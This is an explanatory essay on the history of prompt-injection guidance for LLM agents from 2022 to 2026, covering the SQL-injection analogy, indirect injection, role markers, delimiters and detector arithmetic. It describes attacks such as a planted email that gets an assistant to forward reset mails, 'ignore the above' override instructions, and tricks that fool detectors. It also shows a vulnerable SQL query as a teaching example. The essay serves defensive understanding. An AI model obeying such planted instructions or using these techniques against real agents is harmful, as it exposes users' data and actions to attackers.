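# How security guidance for LLM agents formed outside academic research, 2022 to 2026

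## Prompt injection, agent permissions and the sources of advice

Prompt injection is an attack on software that runs on a large language model (LLM), a program that continues whatever text it receives. The attacker plants instructions in text that the software will pass to the model, and the software then acts on them as though its owner or user had written them. When LLM software could only produce text, the usual result was a silly answer. In *Prompt injection*, Simon Willison (2023), an open-source developer whose blog has followed the problem since 2022, gave the example of a translation program that answers in pirate slang because its input contained an instruction to do so. He conceded that this does little damage, but he worried that developers had begun to connect models to mailboxes, databases and other programs, where a planted instruction could trigger actions.

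Since September 2022, most advice on prompt injection has come from outside academic research. Engineers wrote blog posts, security testers gave conference talks, AI companies added warnings to their product documentation, and OWASP (the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, a volunteer non-profit) put prompt injection at the top of its list of LLM risks. This advice told developers how to word their instructions, what to filter, which permissions to grant and when an agent should ask a person before acting. On 1 May 2026, the US cybersecurity agency CISA, the US National Security Agency and agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom released joint advice on adopting AI agents (CISA, 2026). By then developers had been relying on the informal advice for more than three years, so it matters whether that advice was right.

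### One stream of text

An LLM has a single input, the context window, which is the text it reads at once. Before each step, the application assembles this text by joining several pieces end to end. The developer's instructions, called the system prompt, usually come first. The user's request follows, then anything the application has retrieved to help with it, such as a web page, a document or earlier messages. The application splits the combined text into tokens, which are words or fragments of words. The model computes a likely next token, adds it to the sequence, and repeats.

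A language model processes instructions and data in the same way. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, wrote in a December 2025 post, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, that under the hood "there is only ever 'next token'". A database can be designed to keep commands separate from data, which is why SQL injection, an older attack, has a reliable fix and prompt injection so far does not.

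Makers of chat models use special markers to show where the developer's instructions, the user's words and a tool's output begin and end, and they train the model to rank the developer above the user and the user above retrieved text. But the markers are only more tokens in the same sequence, and their influence depends on what the model learned in training. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) measured that influence by wrapping identical passages of ordinary web text in each of five role markers. A simple classifier was then trained to tell from a model's internal activity which marker surrounded a passage. Because the passages were identical, the classifier could learn only from the markers' effect on that activity.

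They then applied the classifier to a short conversation about gardening. Passages in the style of the model's own reasoning scored 85% as reasoning under the correct markers, 83% with all markers removed, and 85% with the entire conversation marked as the user's words. Changing the markers barely affected the score, which depended mainly on the style of the writing. The same measurement predicted how often attacks succeeded. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where the classifier measured the least confusion about roles to 70% where it measured the most.

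These results suggest that the "next token" formula is slightly too strong. The classifier could read the markers from the model's internal activity, so some distinction between sources exists there. But wording that points the other way overrides that distinction, and the attacker chooses the wording. Whether the distinction is weak or absent makes no difference to someone deciding today what a model may access. It could matter later, because better training might strengthen a weak distinction, but it is harder to see how training could help if there were none. David C leaves this open, writing only that prompt injection "may never be totally mitigated".

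### The email assistant

In 2023, Willison used the example of an assistant that reads and answers a person's email, which he took from a working prototype by another developer, Justin Alvey. Willison (2025) named a hypothetical version of it Marvin in *My Lethal Trifecta talk at the Bay Area AI Security Meetup*.

The developer's instructions describe the job and list the tools. A tool is a function, such as searching the mailbox or reading, sending or deleting a message, that the model can request by writing its name and details in an agreed format. The model only writes the request. A surrounding program, which engineers call the harness, detects the request, runs the function with the user's login, and adds the result to the context window for the model to continue from.

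Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarize new mail. The model outputs a request for the unread messages, the harness fetches them and adds their text to the model's input, and the model writes the summary. But one of those messages could be from a stranger and contain instructions for the assistant to find the user's password-reset emails, forward them to an outside address and delete the traces. These instructions appear in the same sequence as the user's own request. If the model follows them, it outputs a well-formed request to send mail, and the harness carries it out. Security practitioners call this data exfiltration, the movement of private data to a place where an attacker can read it.

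The assistant is an agent in the sense that engineers have settled on. *I think "agent" may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition* (Willison, 2025) defines the term as "An LLM agent runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal". Willison had avoided the word for years and had once gathered 211 definitions of it on Twitter. His definition is close to one he heard in May 2025 from Hannah Moran of the AI company Anthropic, at a developer conference where, he complained, speaker after speaker used the word without defining it (Willison, 2025). Business people often use "agent" to mean a replacement for a member of staff, which doesn't help in deciding what the software should be allowed to access.

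The stranger's email is an example of indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker writes something that the assistant will later read. In direct prompt injection, the attacker is the user, who types instructions meant to override the developer's. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST, 2025) makes the same distinction and adds that an indirect attack often harms the person the software is working for, who has done nothing unusual and may not notice anything wrong.

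A jailbreak is something else again. Here the user tries to make a model break its own maker's rules, for instance by coaxing it into explaining how to make a weapon. It needs no email, no tools and no third party. Usage varies, and the NIST taxonomy files jailbreaks under "direct prompting attacks", next to direct injection, while Willison insists on keeping the two apart. He has a practical reason. As Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, explains, developers who take prompt injection to mean jailbreaking conclude that it can only embarrass the company that made the model, and ignore it. (The trifecta of the title is a combination of abilities that he advises against giving to one agent.)

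The assistant was what computer security has long called a confused deputy, a program tricked into using its authority on behalf of someone who lacks it. The stranger had no right to send mail from the user's account, but the assistant did, and the stranger got it to use that right by asking. David C argues that ordinary confused deputies can be fixed but that an LLM is "inherently confusable", so the sensible aim is to reduce the risk and limit the damage.

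### Limiting what the assistant can do

NIST likewise suggests designing systems on the assumption that a model may leak any sensitive data it can access and misuse any power it has to act. Three measures recur in the guidance, and the email assistant example illustrates the drawbacks of each.

Least privilege means giving a program only the access that its task requires. An assistant that summarizes email needs only a reading tool, and without a sending tool it cannot forward anything, however cleverly a stranger words a message. But the user also wanted the assistant to reply, which requires a sending tool. David C describes a more flexible rule from a conversation on X between Willison and Baibhav Bista. Under this rule, while an LLM processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. The rule is attractively simple but severe. Followed to the letter, it would stop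 the assistant from reading a stranger's message and answering it in one go, which is much of what people would want an email assistant for.

An approval prompt asks a person to confirm an action before it runs. In 2023, Willison recommended that an assistant show the user each email before sending it. He noted in the same passage that an attacker could get around this by having the assistant display a link with private data in its address, which leaks the data when the user clicks. A prompt that appears only before an email is sent would not catch this. Approval prompts also depend on the user reading each one, even after seeing dozens of them.

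A sandbox uses the operating system or the network to limit what a program can reach. It does little for the email assistant. Network rules could restrict the assistant to the mail server, but the stolen messages would leave through that server. A sandbox helps more when an agent runs code on someone's laptop and doesn't need most of the disk or most of the internet. Even then, the agent must not be able to change the sandbox's limits. In a talk covered by Infosecurity Magazine's *Infosecurity Europe* (2026), the OWASP contributor Ariel Fogel described attacks in which an agent's output changed the limits of its sandbox, and others in which a list of pre-approved commands helped the attacker because it already included the commands the agent needed. Fogel works for a security vendor, Pillar Security, and the magazine doesn't name any products, so these reports are more like leads to investigate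 than findings.

### How the advice travels

Software security had ways of spreading warnings long before LLMs. The most rigorous begins with vulnerability disclosure, in which a tester who finds a flaw reports it privately to the vendor, allows time for a repair (90 days is a common limit), and then publishes. The vendor's engineers normally try to reproduce the attack, so a confirmed report describes an attack that worked against a real product. Many confirmed flaws also receive a CVE record, a numbered entry in the public Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures catalogue that identifies the product and usually the affected versions. Many vendors can issue these numbers for their own products.

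This machinery works for a single flaw in a single product, but it handles prompt injection poorly. Willison reviewed two years of reported data thefts from AI products and found that vendors had fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route the data took out. Such a fix can close a CVE record, but the model still has trouble telling sources apart. That weakness is not confined to one product, and no version number marks where it ends.

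The other channels have looser checks. A conference committee typically chooses talks from written proposals and does not repeat the demonstrations. Some talks are never recorded, including Willison's in August 2025, which reached most of its audience as annotated slides on his blog. OWASP's volunteers debate their lists in public, and the ranking reflects their collective judgement more than measurement. Vendor documentation is best placed to reach developers while they are building something, but the vendor has a product to sell and can change the page at any time. A blog post is checked only by its readers, after publication.

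In academic peer review, by contrast, experts who had no part in a study spend some months reading its methods and weighing its claims against its data before a journal or conference accepts it. They rarely rerun the experiments, which is a serious gap in this field. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 recent defences, several of them from peer-reviewed papers. Most were originally reported to hold attackers to success rates near zero, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

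Public discussion can also correct errors that peer review missed. Sander Schulhoff had published a peer-reviewed paper on a prompt-hacking competition and had thought jailbreaking was a type of prompt injection. A discussion on X changed his mind, and he published a post, *Prompt Injection VS Jailbreaking* (2024), with new definitions and an explanation of his mistake. Official documents get corrected too. NIST published its taxonomy, *Adversarial Machine Learning* by Vassilev, Oprea and colleagues (2025), in March 2025, released a corrected file in April, and in June posted a notice of another error to be fixed in a future revision.

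Advice passes between these channels. The attack paper by Nasr and colleagues has authors from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. Willison (2025) summarised it for working developers in *New prompt injection papers* about three weeks after its date. David C's post for the British government draws on the same paper, two academic papers about system design, and the exchange on X.

### Three tests of accuracy

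Each piece of security guidance has to be judged separately on whether it is right about the cause of a problem, whether its proposed fix works, and whether it directs attention to the right place, because it can pass one of these tests and fail another.

The advice attributed prompt injection to LLMs' inability to reliably separate instructions from data, and that diagnosis has held up well against later evidence. In 2025, NIST identified the shared channel for instructions and data as the root of many LLM security flaws. OpenAI's chief information security officer called prompt injection an unsolved problem that October, and Fogel was still describing it as an unsolved problem of architecture in 2026. This agreement is weaker evidence than it looks, because these people read each other (David C's post links to Willison's from 2022). The measurements by Ye and colleagues are stronger evidence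 because they could have contradicted the diagnosis.

Another test is whether the recommended measure withstood adaptive attacks, which are designed with knowledge of the defence. Many evaluations replay a fixed list of old attack texts and report the attack success rate, the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal. A low rate then shows only that the defence stops known attacks. An adaptive attacker tries a text, observes how the defended system responds, revises the text and tries again. Nasr and colleagues automated this loop in several ways and ran a competition with more than 500 human participants. They hold that a defence is not robust if it fails against any version of the loop.

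That standard is right for a measure presented as a solution. It is harsh on one meant only to make attacks more difficult, because Nasr and colleagues assumed an attacker with ample computing power and did not try to find out how hard each defence was to break. Limits on permissions have to be tested differently. No wording can restore a sending tool that the harness does not have, so the tester has to look for another route to the same harm, such as the link that the user clicks.

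The remaining test, whether recorded harm occurred where the guidance said it would, is the hardest to apply because the records are uneven. Willison's list of products open to data theft has fourteen entries between April 2023 and February 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and Microsoft Copilot. The entries are reports of successful attacks, mostly from researchers, and they show that theft was possible but not that any customer lost data. Demonstrations, attacks by criminals and accidents with no attacker therefore need separate counts. Some of these counts will be more complete than others, because people notice the same day when an agent wipes a database, but may never find out that an assistant forwarded three emails and deleted the copies. A short list of known thefts is poor evidence that a warning was exaggerated, unless somebody could have detected the thefts.

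## The naming of prompt injection and the comparison with SQL injection

The name "prompt injection" spread through a September 2022 blog post that compared the problem to SQL injection, an attack web developers had dealt with since the 1990s. The comparison helped them understand the problem quickly, but it also encouraged a belief that careful programming would fix it, which took years to fade.

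### September 2022

By 2022, companies could build OpenAI's GPT-3, a language model released two years earlier, into their own products through a paid interface. Around 11 September that year, Riley Goodside, a data researcher, published experiments with GPT-3 on Twitter. Goodside asked the model to translate an English text into French. The text contained an instruction to ignore the directions above it and give a taunt as the translation, and GPT-3 produced the taunt. Goodside then tried the obvious defence of adding a warning that the text might contain tricks and an instruction to translate it regardless, but GPT-3 produced the taunt again.

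The next day, in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, Willison (2022) argued that this was a security flaw and proposed calling it "prompt injection". Like Goodside's example, products built on GPT-3 joined a fixed instruction to whatever the user typed, so any user could try to replace the instruction. Willison added his own attack, which made a translation program print the developer's instructions. He expected some start-ups to regard such instructions as a trade secret.

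He took the name from SQL injection. SQL is the language in which programs send requests to a database, and a careless program builds a request by joining strings:

```
query = "SELECT email FROM members WHERE name = '" + name + "'"
```

The single quotation marks tell the database where the name begins and ends. If a visitor enters the name O'Brien, the apostrophe ends the name after the O, and the database tries to read the remaining letters as part of the command. It fails and reports an error. An attacker puts something after the apostrophe that the database can read, such as a command to delete the table. The remedy is a parameterised query, in which the developer marks the place for the name and passes the name separately:

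```
query = "SELECT email FROM members WHERE name = ?"
cursor.execute(query, [name])
```

Now the database searches for a member called O'Brien, apostrophe included, and treats an attacker's command as a name too. In SQL's formal grammar, the question mark can stand only for a value, so nothing a visitor types there can become a command.

Willison wanted the same for language models, an interface with one parameter for the instruction and others for the data, but he did not know whether anyone could build it. Prompted by a reader, Niel Thiart, he soon added a note that one OpenAI model already had separate fields for instruction and input, and that attacks through the input field still worked. Separate fields alone were therefore not enough. They protect a database because the software behind them handles their contents differently, which OpenAI's model evidently did not do reliably.

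On 15 September, Twitter users found that they could manipulate a GPT-3 bot that Remoteli.io, a remote jobs site, ran to reply to tweets about remote work. They got it to call a US senator the Zodiac Killer, threaten the president and, as Gizmodo reported, claim responsibility for the Challenger shuttle disaster. It also disclosed its instructions, which told it to be positive about remote work and to write as "we". According to Ars Technica's *Twitter pranksters derail GPT-3 bot with newly discovered “prompt injection” hack* (2022), hundreds of people joined in before the bot shut down. None of them needed to write code. The harm was mostly embarrassment, and Willison told the reporter that an attack probably didn't matter if only the attacker saw the result.

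In *I don't know how to solve prompt injection*, published on 16 September, Willison (2022) wrote that he knew how to beat SQL injection and many other attacks but had "no idea how to reliably beat prompt injection". He quoted Glyph, a programmer with security experience, who explained that the fixes for those older attacks correct syntax errors, whereas a prompt has no formal syntax to correct. Tests could not show that a defence was reliable either, because a developer can never try every sentence an attacker might write, and each new version of a model might respond differently to the same sentences. Willison also argued that a defence that works 99% of the time is inadequate, because somebody will eventually find an attack that gets past it.

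The 99% argument is sound where attackers can keep trying without consequences, as they could with the bot, but it is weaker where failed attempts leave traces. David C later advised operators to log failed tool calls, because an attacker will probably have to refine an attack before it works, and the early attempts may reveal it.

Willison still hoped that model makers would provide the remedy the comparison suggested, a clean separation between instructions and user input, with formal research to prove that it held. He gave up on this remedy in April 2023, seven months after the post that introduced the name, when he added a note to that post saying that such a separation looked "extremely difficult, if not impossible" with current language model designs.

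### Who was first

Preamble, an AI safety start-up, found the flaw before Goodside and Willison. According to its *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022), the company emailed OpenAI about it on 3 May 2022 and received a confirmation within 30 minutes. It sent more examples the next day and ideas for reducing the risk on 19 May. Preamble made this correspondence public only on 22 September, ten days after Willison's post.

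The name and the comparison with SQL injection also predated Willison's use of them. On 13 May 2022, a Twitter user called @himbodhisattva asked whether services built on GPT-3 were open to an equivalent of SQL injection, "like, a prompt-injection attack?" Willison later credited this user with coining the term four months before he did.

Preamble's dates come from its own account, and a young company benefits from being credited with a discovery. But its claim has some support from before the subject became popular. Days before Goodside's tweets, Branch, Rodriguez Cefalu and colleagues (2022), most of whom worked at Preamble, described the attack in *Evaluating the Susceptibility of Pre-Trained Language Models via Handcrafted Adversarial Examples* and mentioned a report to OpenAI.

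Their paper helps to explain why Preamble did not set the vocabulary, since a developer building a chatbot would have seen little in it that resembled their product. Branch and colleagues wrote 40 inputs that told a model to ignore its instructions and classify something wrongly. In the example they show, GPT-3 favoured the planted answer over the correct one by a margin of nearly 14%. They also tested three older models that fill in blanks in a text, and the planted answer won 42.5% of the time with one and 67.5% with each of the other two. These figures are hard to interpret, because a model that fills in blanks may choose a word because it stands nearby. Much of the paper tests whether standard measures of textual similarity detect the changed answers, which they mostly do not. Branch and colleagues recommend further training.

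Willison wrote for that developer, using the kind of code his readers wrote themselves and examples they could repeat within minutes on OpenAI's public test page. The timing also helped, since the Remoteli.io bot failed in public three days later and reporters needed a name for what had happened. Hackaday, a site for hardware and software hobbyists, called the problem "SQL injection in a nutshell".

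On 22 September, the well-known security writer Bruce Schneier covered the attack on his blog. Schneier (2022), in *Prompt Injection/Extraction Attacks against AI Systems*, called it an attack "I had not previously considered". Preamble's Jon Cefalu claimed the discovery in the comments the following night. He also promoted the company's phrase "Harvard Architecture Language Model", after a type of computer that keeps instructions and data in separate memories. Like Willison with his two parameters, Cefalu hoped to separate instructions from data, but hardly anyone adopted the phrase. In December, Selvi (2022), in *Exploring Prompt Injection Attacks*, a post for the security firm NCC Group, credited Cefalu with the first report and Goodside with the first public release, but used Willison's name for the attack. Preamble also uses that name. Willison has kept it in circulation, with at least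 163 posts under that tag.

Private reporting therefore gave Preamble the best claim to the discovery but little influence on how people talked about it. Preamble's *Responsible Disclosure of AI Vulnerabilities* explains that the flaw was still open months later because it had no quick fix. If Preamble had made the flaw public in May, developers could at least have limited what their programs were able to do, even without a fix from OpenAI.

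Academic papers often assign credit differently. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) attributes the first demonstration to Fábio Perez and Ian Ribeiro. This is chronologically wrong, since their paper appeared on 17 November 2022, two months after Goodside's tweets, but Perez and Ribeiro did contribute something that the tweets and blog posts lacked.

### Counting successes

Perez and Ribeiro (2022), in *Ignore Previous Prompt*, measured how often the attack worked on 35 sample applications from OpenAI's website. They assembled each attack from interchangeable parts: a command to disregard the instructions, a row of separating characters, and a phrase for the model to print. They called it goal hijacking when the model printed the attacker's phrase instead of performing its task, and prompt leaking when it revealed the developer's instructions. Later works, including *Survey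 of Vulnerabilities in Large Language Models Revealed by Adversarial Attacks* (2023), adopted this division.

Goal hijacking succeeded 58.6% of the time with the newest GPT-3 model and a hostile phrase. The rate fell to 43.6% without the separating characters and rose to 70% with a harmless phrase. Prompt leaking succeeded only 2.9% of the time in its plainest form, but 23.6% after Perez and Ribeiro disguised the request as a spelling check, so a developer who tested only the plain version would have underestimated the risk.

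They also found that the newest model was the most vulnerable of the five they tested. Attacks succeeded against its predecessor 30.5% of the time and against the smallest model 13.8% of the time. Five models are too few to establish a general rule, and vulnerability did not always increase with size. Still, it is plausible that a model that is better at following instructions may also be better at following an attacker's. If so, developers could not expect the problem to disappear as models improved.

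Perez and Ribeiro studied only attacks by malicious users, which left open how serious prompt injection was. A commenter on Hackaday had argued in September that it was "no comparison" with SQL injection, a fair objection for a translation program. An attacker who gets into a database can damage other people's data, whereas people who attacked GPT-3 had affected only their own sessions.

### Instructions from a third party

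The objection stopped being convincing in February 2023, when *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) pointed out that developers were connecting language models to search engines and mailboxes, which gave attackers a way to reach other people's assistants. The paper, most of whose authors worked at German research institutions, introduced the term "indirect prompt injection" for this kind of attack. It argued that a model reading untrusted material is like a computer running a stranger's program.

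The researchers built mock assistants that could search, read web pages, handle email, consult an address book and keep notes. The tools returned prepared content, so the assistants could not reach any real system. In one demonstration, a malicious email caused an assistant to look up the user's contacts and forward the email to them, where it could spread through other assistants like a computer worm. In another, an assistant saved the attacker's instructions in its notes. After a reset, it behaved normally until the user asked it to read the last conversation from its notes, and then it followed the instructions again. The researchers also made an assistant fetch new instructions from a mock attacker's server, which would let an attacker change the plan after the first break-in.

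After Microsoft launched Bing Chat, a search assistant built on GPT-4, the researchers could test their attacks on a real product. Bing Chat could read whatever page the user had open in the browser, so they hid instructions in pages stored on their own computers. In one session, they instructed Bing Chat to find out the user's real name without raising suspicion. The instructions did not specify which topics or tactics to use. When the user asked about the weather, Bing Chat answered and then asked about the user's plans and work. The user, playing a journalist, later gave a name, and Bing Chat offered a link that contained a scrambled version of it. In other tests, Bing Chat promoted a fake gift card, denied that Einstein had won a Nobel Prize, and left the *New York Times* out of its news summaries.

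Bing Chat ended the conversation when a user typed a known jailbreak, but it obeyed similar text in a web page. Microsoft seemed to be filtering what users typed and what the model answered, but to have overlooked the material the model retrieved.

These demonstrations proved that the attack was possible on a widely used product, but not how often it would work. Greshake and colleagues reported no success rates, because the conversations varied too much for simple scoring, and said only that many of their attacks had worked on the first attempt. They avoided planting anything on the public web and had no access to Microsoft's office assistant. In GitHub Copilot, which suggests code to programmers, the planted instructions were much less effective inside larger programs.

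Greshake, Endres and colleagues presented the work at Black Hat USA, a large security conference, in August 2023. In their slides, *Compromising LLMs* (2023), they recalled that the attacks had been speculative when they first posted the paper and had then worked on Bing as predicted. After that, they had informed OpenAI, Microsoft and Germany's federal office for information security. They ended by claiming, "There is no mitigation, and there can be no mitigation." In the paper they had written only that a foolproof solution was hard to imagine. That more cautious claim fits their evidence better, because sandboxing, which they had listed a few slides earlier as a possible approach, can limit the damage even when the model follows the attacker's instructions.

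Practitioners picked up the idea quickly. Willison (2023) recommended both the talk and the paper, which he called the "most thorough review" of such attacks he had seen. Johann Rehberger, a security tester who publishes as Embrace The Red (2023), drew on the same paper to explain indirect injection at HITCON, a hacker conference in Taiwan, and in slides for the Chaos Communication Congress in Germany. The Black Hat slides in turn included Rehberger's attacks on ChatGPT plugins and Google's Bard. Although the idea came from a research paper, many working developers would have first encountered it in a talk or blog post.

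### Where the comparison failed

Indirect injection made prompt injection closer in seriousness to SQL injection, because the victim was now somebody other than the attacker, but there was still no equivalent of the parameterised query. For this reason, David C, writing for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, called the comparison "dangerous". David C had noticed that many security professionals with a background in web applications assumed the two problems were alike. The centre's own warnings may have contributed to this assumption. ThreatDown had reported an earlier one under the headline *Prompt injection could be the SQL injection of the future, warns NCSC*.

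David C's evidence is an impression from conversations with colleagues, but it agrees with the account of Steve Wilson, who founded and co-chairs the project behind OWASP's list of LLM risks. Wilson told the security company ReversingLabs in 2026 that prompt injection had seemed comparable to SQL injection when the list first appeared three years earlier. The people working on the list had thought that enough care could largely prevent prompt injection. Wilson said that this assumption had proved false and that prompt injection was now considered unavoidable.

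Four days after he proposed the name "prompt injection", and well before the first OWASP list, Willison warned that he knew of no reliable remedy. But the name became much better known than the post containing that warning. It reminded developers of SQL injection and its cure, and they had to read further to learn that the same cure did not work for prompt injection.

The misunderstanding misdirected developers' effort. Someone who has learned to prevent SQL injection will look for the correct way to write the prompt, perhaps by putting quotation marks around the untrusted text or filtering suspicious phrases. Willison was already objecting to such measures in September 2022. Writing a query correctly prevents SQL injection, but Jason Soroko of the security company Sectigo told ReversingLabs that with a language model every mitigation "lowers probability without reaching zero". The developer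 therefore still has to decide what the program may do when an attack succeeds.

David C still accepts the historical comparison. Testers described SQL injection in the 1990s, but attacks peaked only around 2010, when databases had become a core part of many websites and few of their owners had dealt with the risk. Better defaults came only after a decade of break-ins. David C fears a similar wave as companies add language models to most of their software, and advises them to distrust any product that claims to "stop" prompt injection. A language model may be unsuitable for a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

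## Advice to mark or filter untrusted text

Developers who hoped to stop prompt injection as they had stopped SQL injection soon had two popular remedies. They could mark untrusted text to signal that the model should not obey it, or they could have another model screen the text first and reject anything that looked like an attack. Both measures stop many attacks, but both leave the final decision to a model that reads the attacker's text and can be misled by it.

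### Markers around untrusted text

On 12 September 2022, the day Willison proposed the name "prompt injection", Goodside suggested marking untrusted text by putting it inside quotation marks, in a format that programs use to exchange data. In his example, GPT-3 then translated the planted instruction instead of obeying it.

OpenAI built a more elaborate kind of marking into its products at the start of March 2023. Developers had previously sent GPT-3 a single block of text. The new ChatGPT interface accepted a list of messages, each with a role such as "system" or "user", and OpenAI's software converted the list into a format called ChatML, in which each message starts with a special marker and the name of its role and ends with another marker. Rickard (2023), in *ChatML and the ChatGPT API*, thought the principles mattered more than the syntax, which was still changing. Labworks' *ChatML*,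 a post by a practitioner, asked in its headline whether the format was the solution to prompt injection. OWASP's first list of LLM risks later recommended ChatML.

ChatML solved the problem of forged markers. If a developer builds the whole prompt as one string, as the sample code in Microsoft's *Chat Markup Language ChatML (Preview)* did, a user can type a marker that closes their own message and then open one that appears to come from the developer. OpenAI's notes on the format warned about this attack and compared it to SQL injection. If the developer sends a list of messages instead, the software can encode any markers the user types as ordinary text, much as a parameterised query handles an apostrophe.

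But a model can ignore even a genuine marker. OpenAI acknowledged in its announcement, which Keshwani quotes in notes on chat formats, that the input was "still rendered to the model as a sequence" of tokens. In August 2024, Willison added a note to an old post, saying that system prompts, which developed from this scheme, had not proved fully reliable against instructions elsewhere in the input.

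Research on role confusion helps explain why role markers can fail. Ye and colleagues found that a passage's style, its position and even plain statements about its source can outweigh the markers, and an attacker can control all three. They took attacks written in the style of a model's private reasoning and reworded them to remove that style but keep the meaning. The role markers stayed the same, and the rewording alone cut the attacks' average success rate from 61% to 10%, according to Willison's summary.

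Many developers learned a simpler version of marking from *ChatGPT Prompt Engineering for Developers*, a 2023 video course that Isa Fulford and Andrew Ng presented in partnership with OpenAI. It taught them to enclose untrusted text in delimiters, ordinary characters such as a row of backticks. In the course's example, the developer asks for a summary of a delimited passage that contains an instruction to write a poem about pandas instead. The presenters said that, because of the delimiters, "the model kind of knows" that it should summarise the instruction and not follow it.

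Willison (2023), in *Delimiters won't save you from prompt injection*, tried the example and got the result that the course promised. He then defeated it by typing the delimiters inside the passage, so that the passage seemed to end early. A developer can prevent this by removing such characters or by choosing random delimiters for each request. Willison's other attack contained no delimiters, so neither precaution would have stopped it. It consisted of a short text, a finished summary, and then a request for a poem. Because the summary appeared to be done, the model went on to write the poem.

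A few trials on one model are enough to refute the claim that the model "knows" what to do, though not to show how often delimiters fail. Willison was especially disappointed that the advice came from OpenAI. To his knowledge, this was the first time the company had published a proposed solution to prompt injection.

Spotlighting, which Microsoft researchers published in 2024, marks the text that an agent's tools return so that the model can tell it apart from the user's request. Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, in case the model is no longer following it. Both methods make the intended task more prominent, but they still depend on the model following that task rather than instructions in the untrusted text.

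### A detector in front of the model

The alternative to marking is a detector, often sold as a "guardrail". When an email arrives, for example, the application sends it to the detector before the assistant's model reads it. The detector scores how closely the email resembles an attack. If the score passes a threshold, the application discards the email or stops the task. Some products also check the assistant's output. Microsoft's Prompt Shields checks both the user's prompt and any accompanying documents. Google's Model Armor is a comparable product, and Meta's PromptGuard is a detector that developers can download and run themselves.

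Many detectors are small language models trained on a mixture of harmless prompts and known attacks, so they learn what past attacks looked like. Schulhoff's *The AI Security Industry is Bullshit* gives an admittedly speculative account of how vendors sell them. The vendor runs an automated attack tool against the customer's model, which reliably produces alarming results, and then offers a guardrail as the fix. The demonstration shows that the customer has a problem, but it is no evidence that the guardrail would stop an attacker who knew about it.

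Willison had objected to the whole approach on 17 September 2022, five days after naming the attack. In *You can't solve AI security problems with more AI*, he considered proposals to screen the input, screen the output, and move the developer's instruction to the end of the prompt. A detector that is itself a language model can also fall for prompt injection. Willison's favourite counterexample was an attack by Marco Bueno that included a second sentence telling the detector to report that no injection had taken place.

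He also raised the problem of false alarms. In the 2000s, some web forums protected themselves by deleting anything that looked like an HTML tag, the code that formats web pages, which made them useless for discussing HTML. A translation service that rejects suspicious text could not translate Willison's own posts about prompt injection. A stricter threshold catches more attacks but also blocks more legitimate text. If an assistant reads 1,000 harmless emails a day and its detector rejects 1% of them, the user loses ten emails a day.

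No threshold can fully resolve this for a detector that checks only the document, because whether a sentence is an attack can depend on what the user asked for. *The Devil is in the Context* (Chang, Nikolić and colleagues, 2026), a paper partly from Microsoft's security response centre, gives the example of a document that asks the reader to send the completed report to an address below. Sending the report is correct if the user wanted the agent to do whatever the document asks, but it means an injection has succeeded if the user wanted a summary.

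They also describe other gaps. An attacker can encode an instruction in a form that the assistant's model can read but a smaller detector cannot. An attacker can also split an attack across two web pages that each look harmless when inspected alone. A detector as capable as the main model might close some of these gaps, but Red Hat's *Beyond guardrails* points out that it would slow every request and use more tokens.

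Some researchers have tried to detect attacks by their effects rather than their wording. Data Sentinel gives a model the suspicious text along with a secret key and tells it to repeat the key and ignore the text. If the model fails to repeat the key, the text has presumably hijacked it. MELON runs the agent twice, replacing the user's request with a harmless summarising task the second time. If both runs produce the same tool calls, the retrieved text probably caused them, and MELON raises an alarm. Both methods assume that an attack will behave the same way during the test as in real use.

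### Why 99% may be too little

Simple arithmetic supports Willison's objection to defences that work 99% of the time. Suppose that a detector stops 99% of attempts, that every attempt it misses succeeds, and that attempts are independent. The chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is then

1 − 0.99ⁿ

The chance that at least one attempt succeeds is about 10% after 10 attempts, 50% after 69, 63% after 100 and 95% after 300. An attacker can also spread the attempts over many people, and one message to each of 10,000 users would produce about 100 successes. Improving the detector to 99.9% raises the number of attempts needed for a 50% chance from 69 to 693, which a program can easily send.

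Real attempts are not independent. A classifier generally classifies identical text the same way, so the attacker has to vary it. Attackers who learn from each rejection will do better than the formula predicts, and those who keep trying similar ideas will do worse. Still, a defence can fail even when the success rate per attempt is low. Damianakis and Psounis (2026), in *SoK*, found that only about 2% of the distinct submissions to two public prompt injection contests achieved their goal, but contestants could fail many times with little consequence.

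Vendors usually reply that nobody should rely on a single detector. When OpenAI launched its Atlas browser in October 2025, its security chief, Dane Stuckey, described "overlapping guardrails and safety measures", together with special training for the model and a system for quickly blocking new attack campaigns. He did not claim that these measures solved the problem. In *Three years later*, a post for the guardrail company Superagent, Zabihi accepts that Willison was "mostly right at the time" but argues that the early detectors were brittle and that developers can now use AI to defend agents meaningfully. Zabihi has a commercial interest in this argument, but the claim that detectors have improved is plausible.

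Layered defenses work best when each layer misses different attacks. If two detectors each miss one attack in 100, and their misses are unrelated, only one attack in 10,000 will get past both. But detectors trained on similar collections of old attacks tend to miss similar attacks, so a text that gets past one is more likely than most to get past the next. Adding a different kind of control therefore helps more than adding another detector.

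*The Economist* made a related argument from civil engineering. Victorian engineers built in tolerances and redundancy because they could not be sure how strong their materials were, and software developers could do the same with unreliable models. Willison (2025), in *How to stop AI’s “lethal trifecta”*, mostly agreed. The analogy holds for a model's ordinary mistakes but not for attacks, because attackers deliberately look for a system's weakest point.

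Willison (2025) also answers the common remark that no security fix works 100% of the time. He argues that parameterised queries do when developers use them correctly, and that a mistake in using them has a known repair. This is a fair answer to anyone who calls a detector a fix, but it is less decisive for a developer who has no equivalent of the parameterised query and must choose between a detector and nothing. Willison conceded in 2022 that protection of about 95% might be good enough for some applications.

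How easily an attacker can retry depends on the deployment. OpenAI can watch for suspicious patterns across all its users, which shortens the useful life of a new attack. But if the detector can be downloaded, as PromptGuard can, an attacker can test thousands of versions of an attack on their own computer, where nobody sees the failures.

### Attacks designed for the defence

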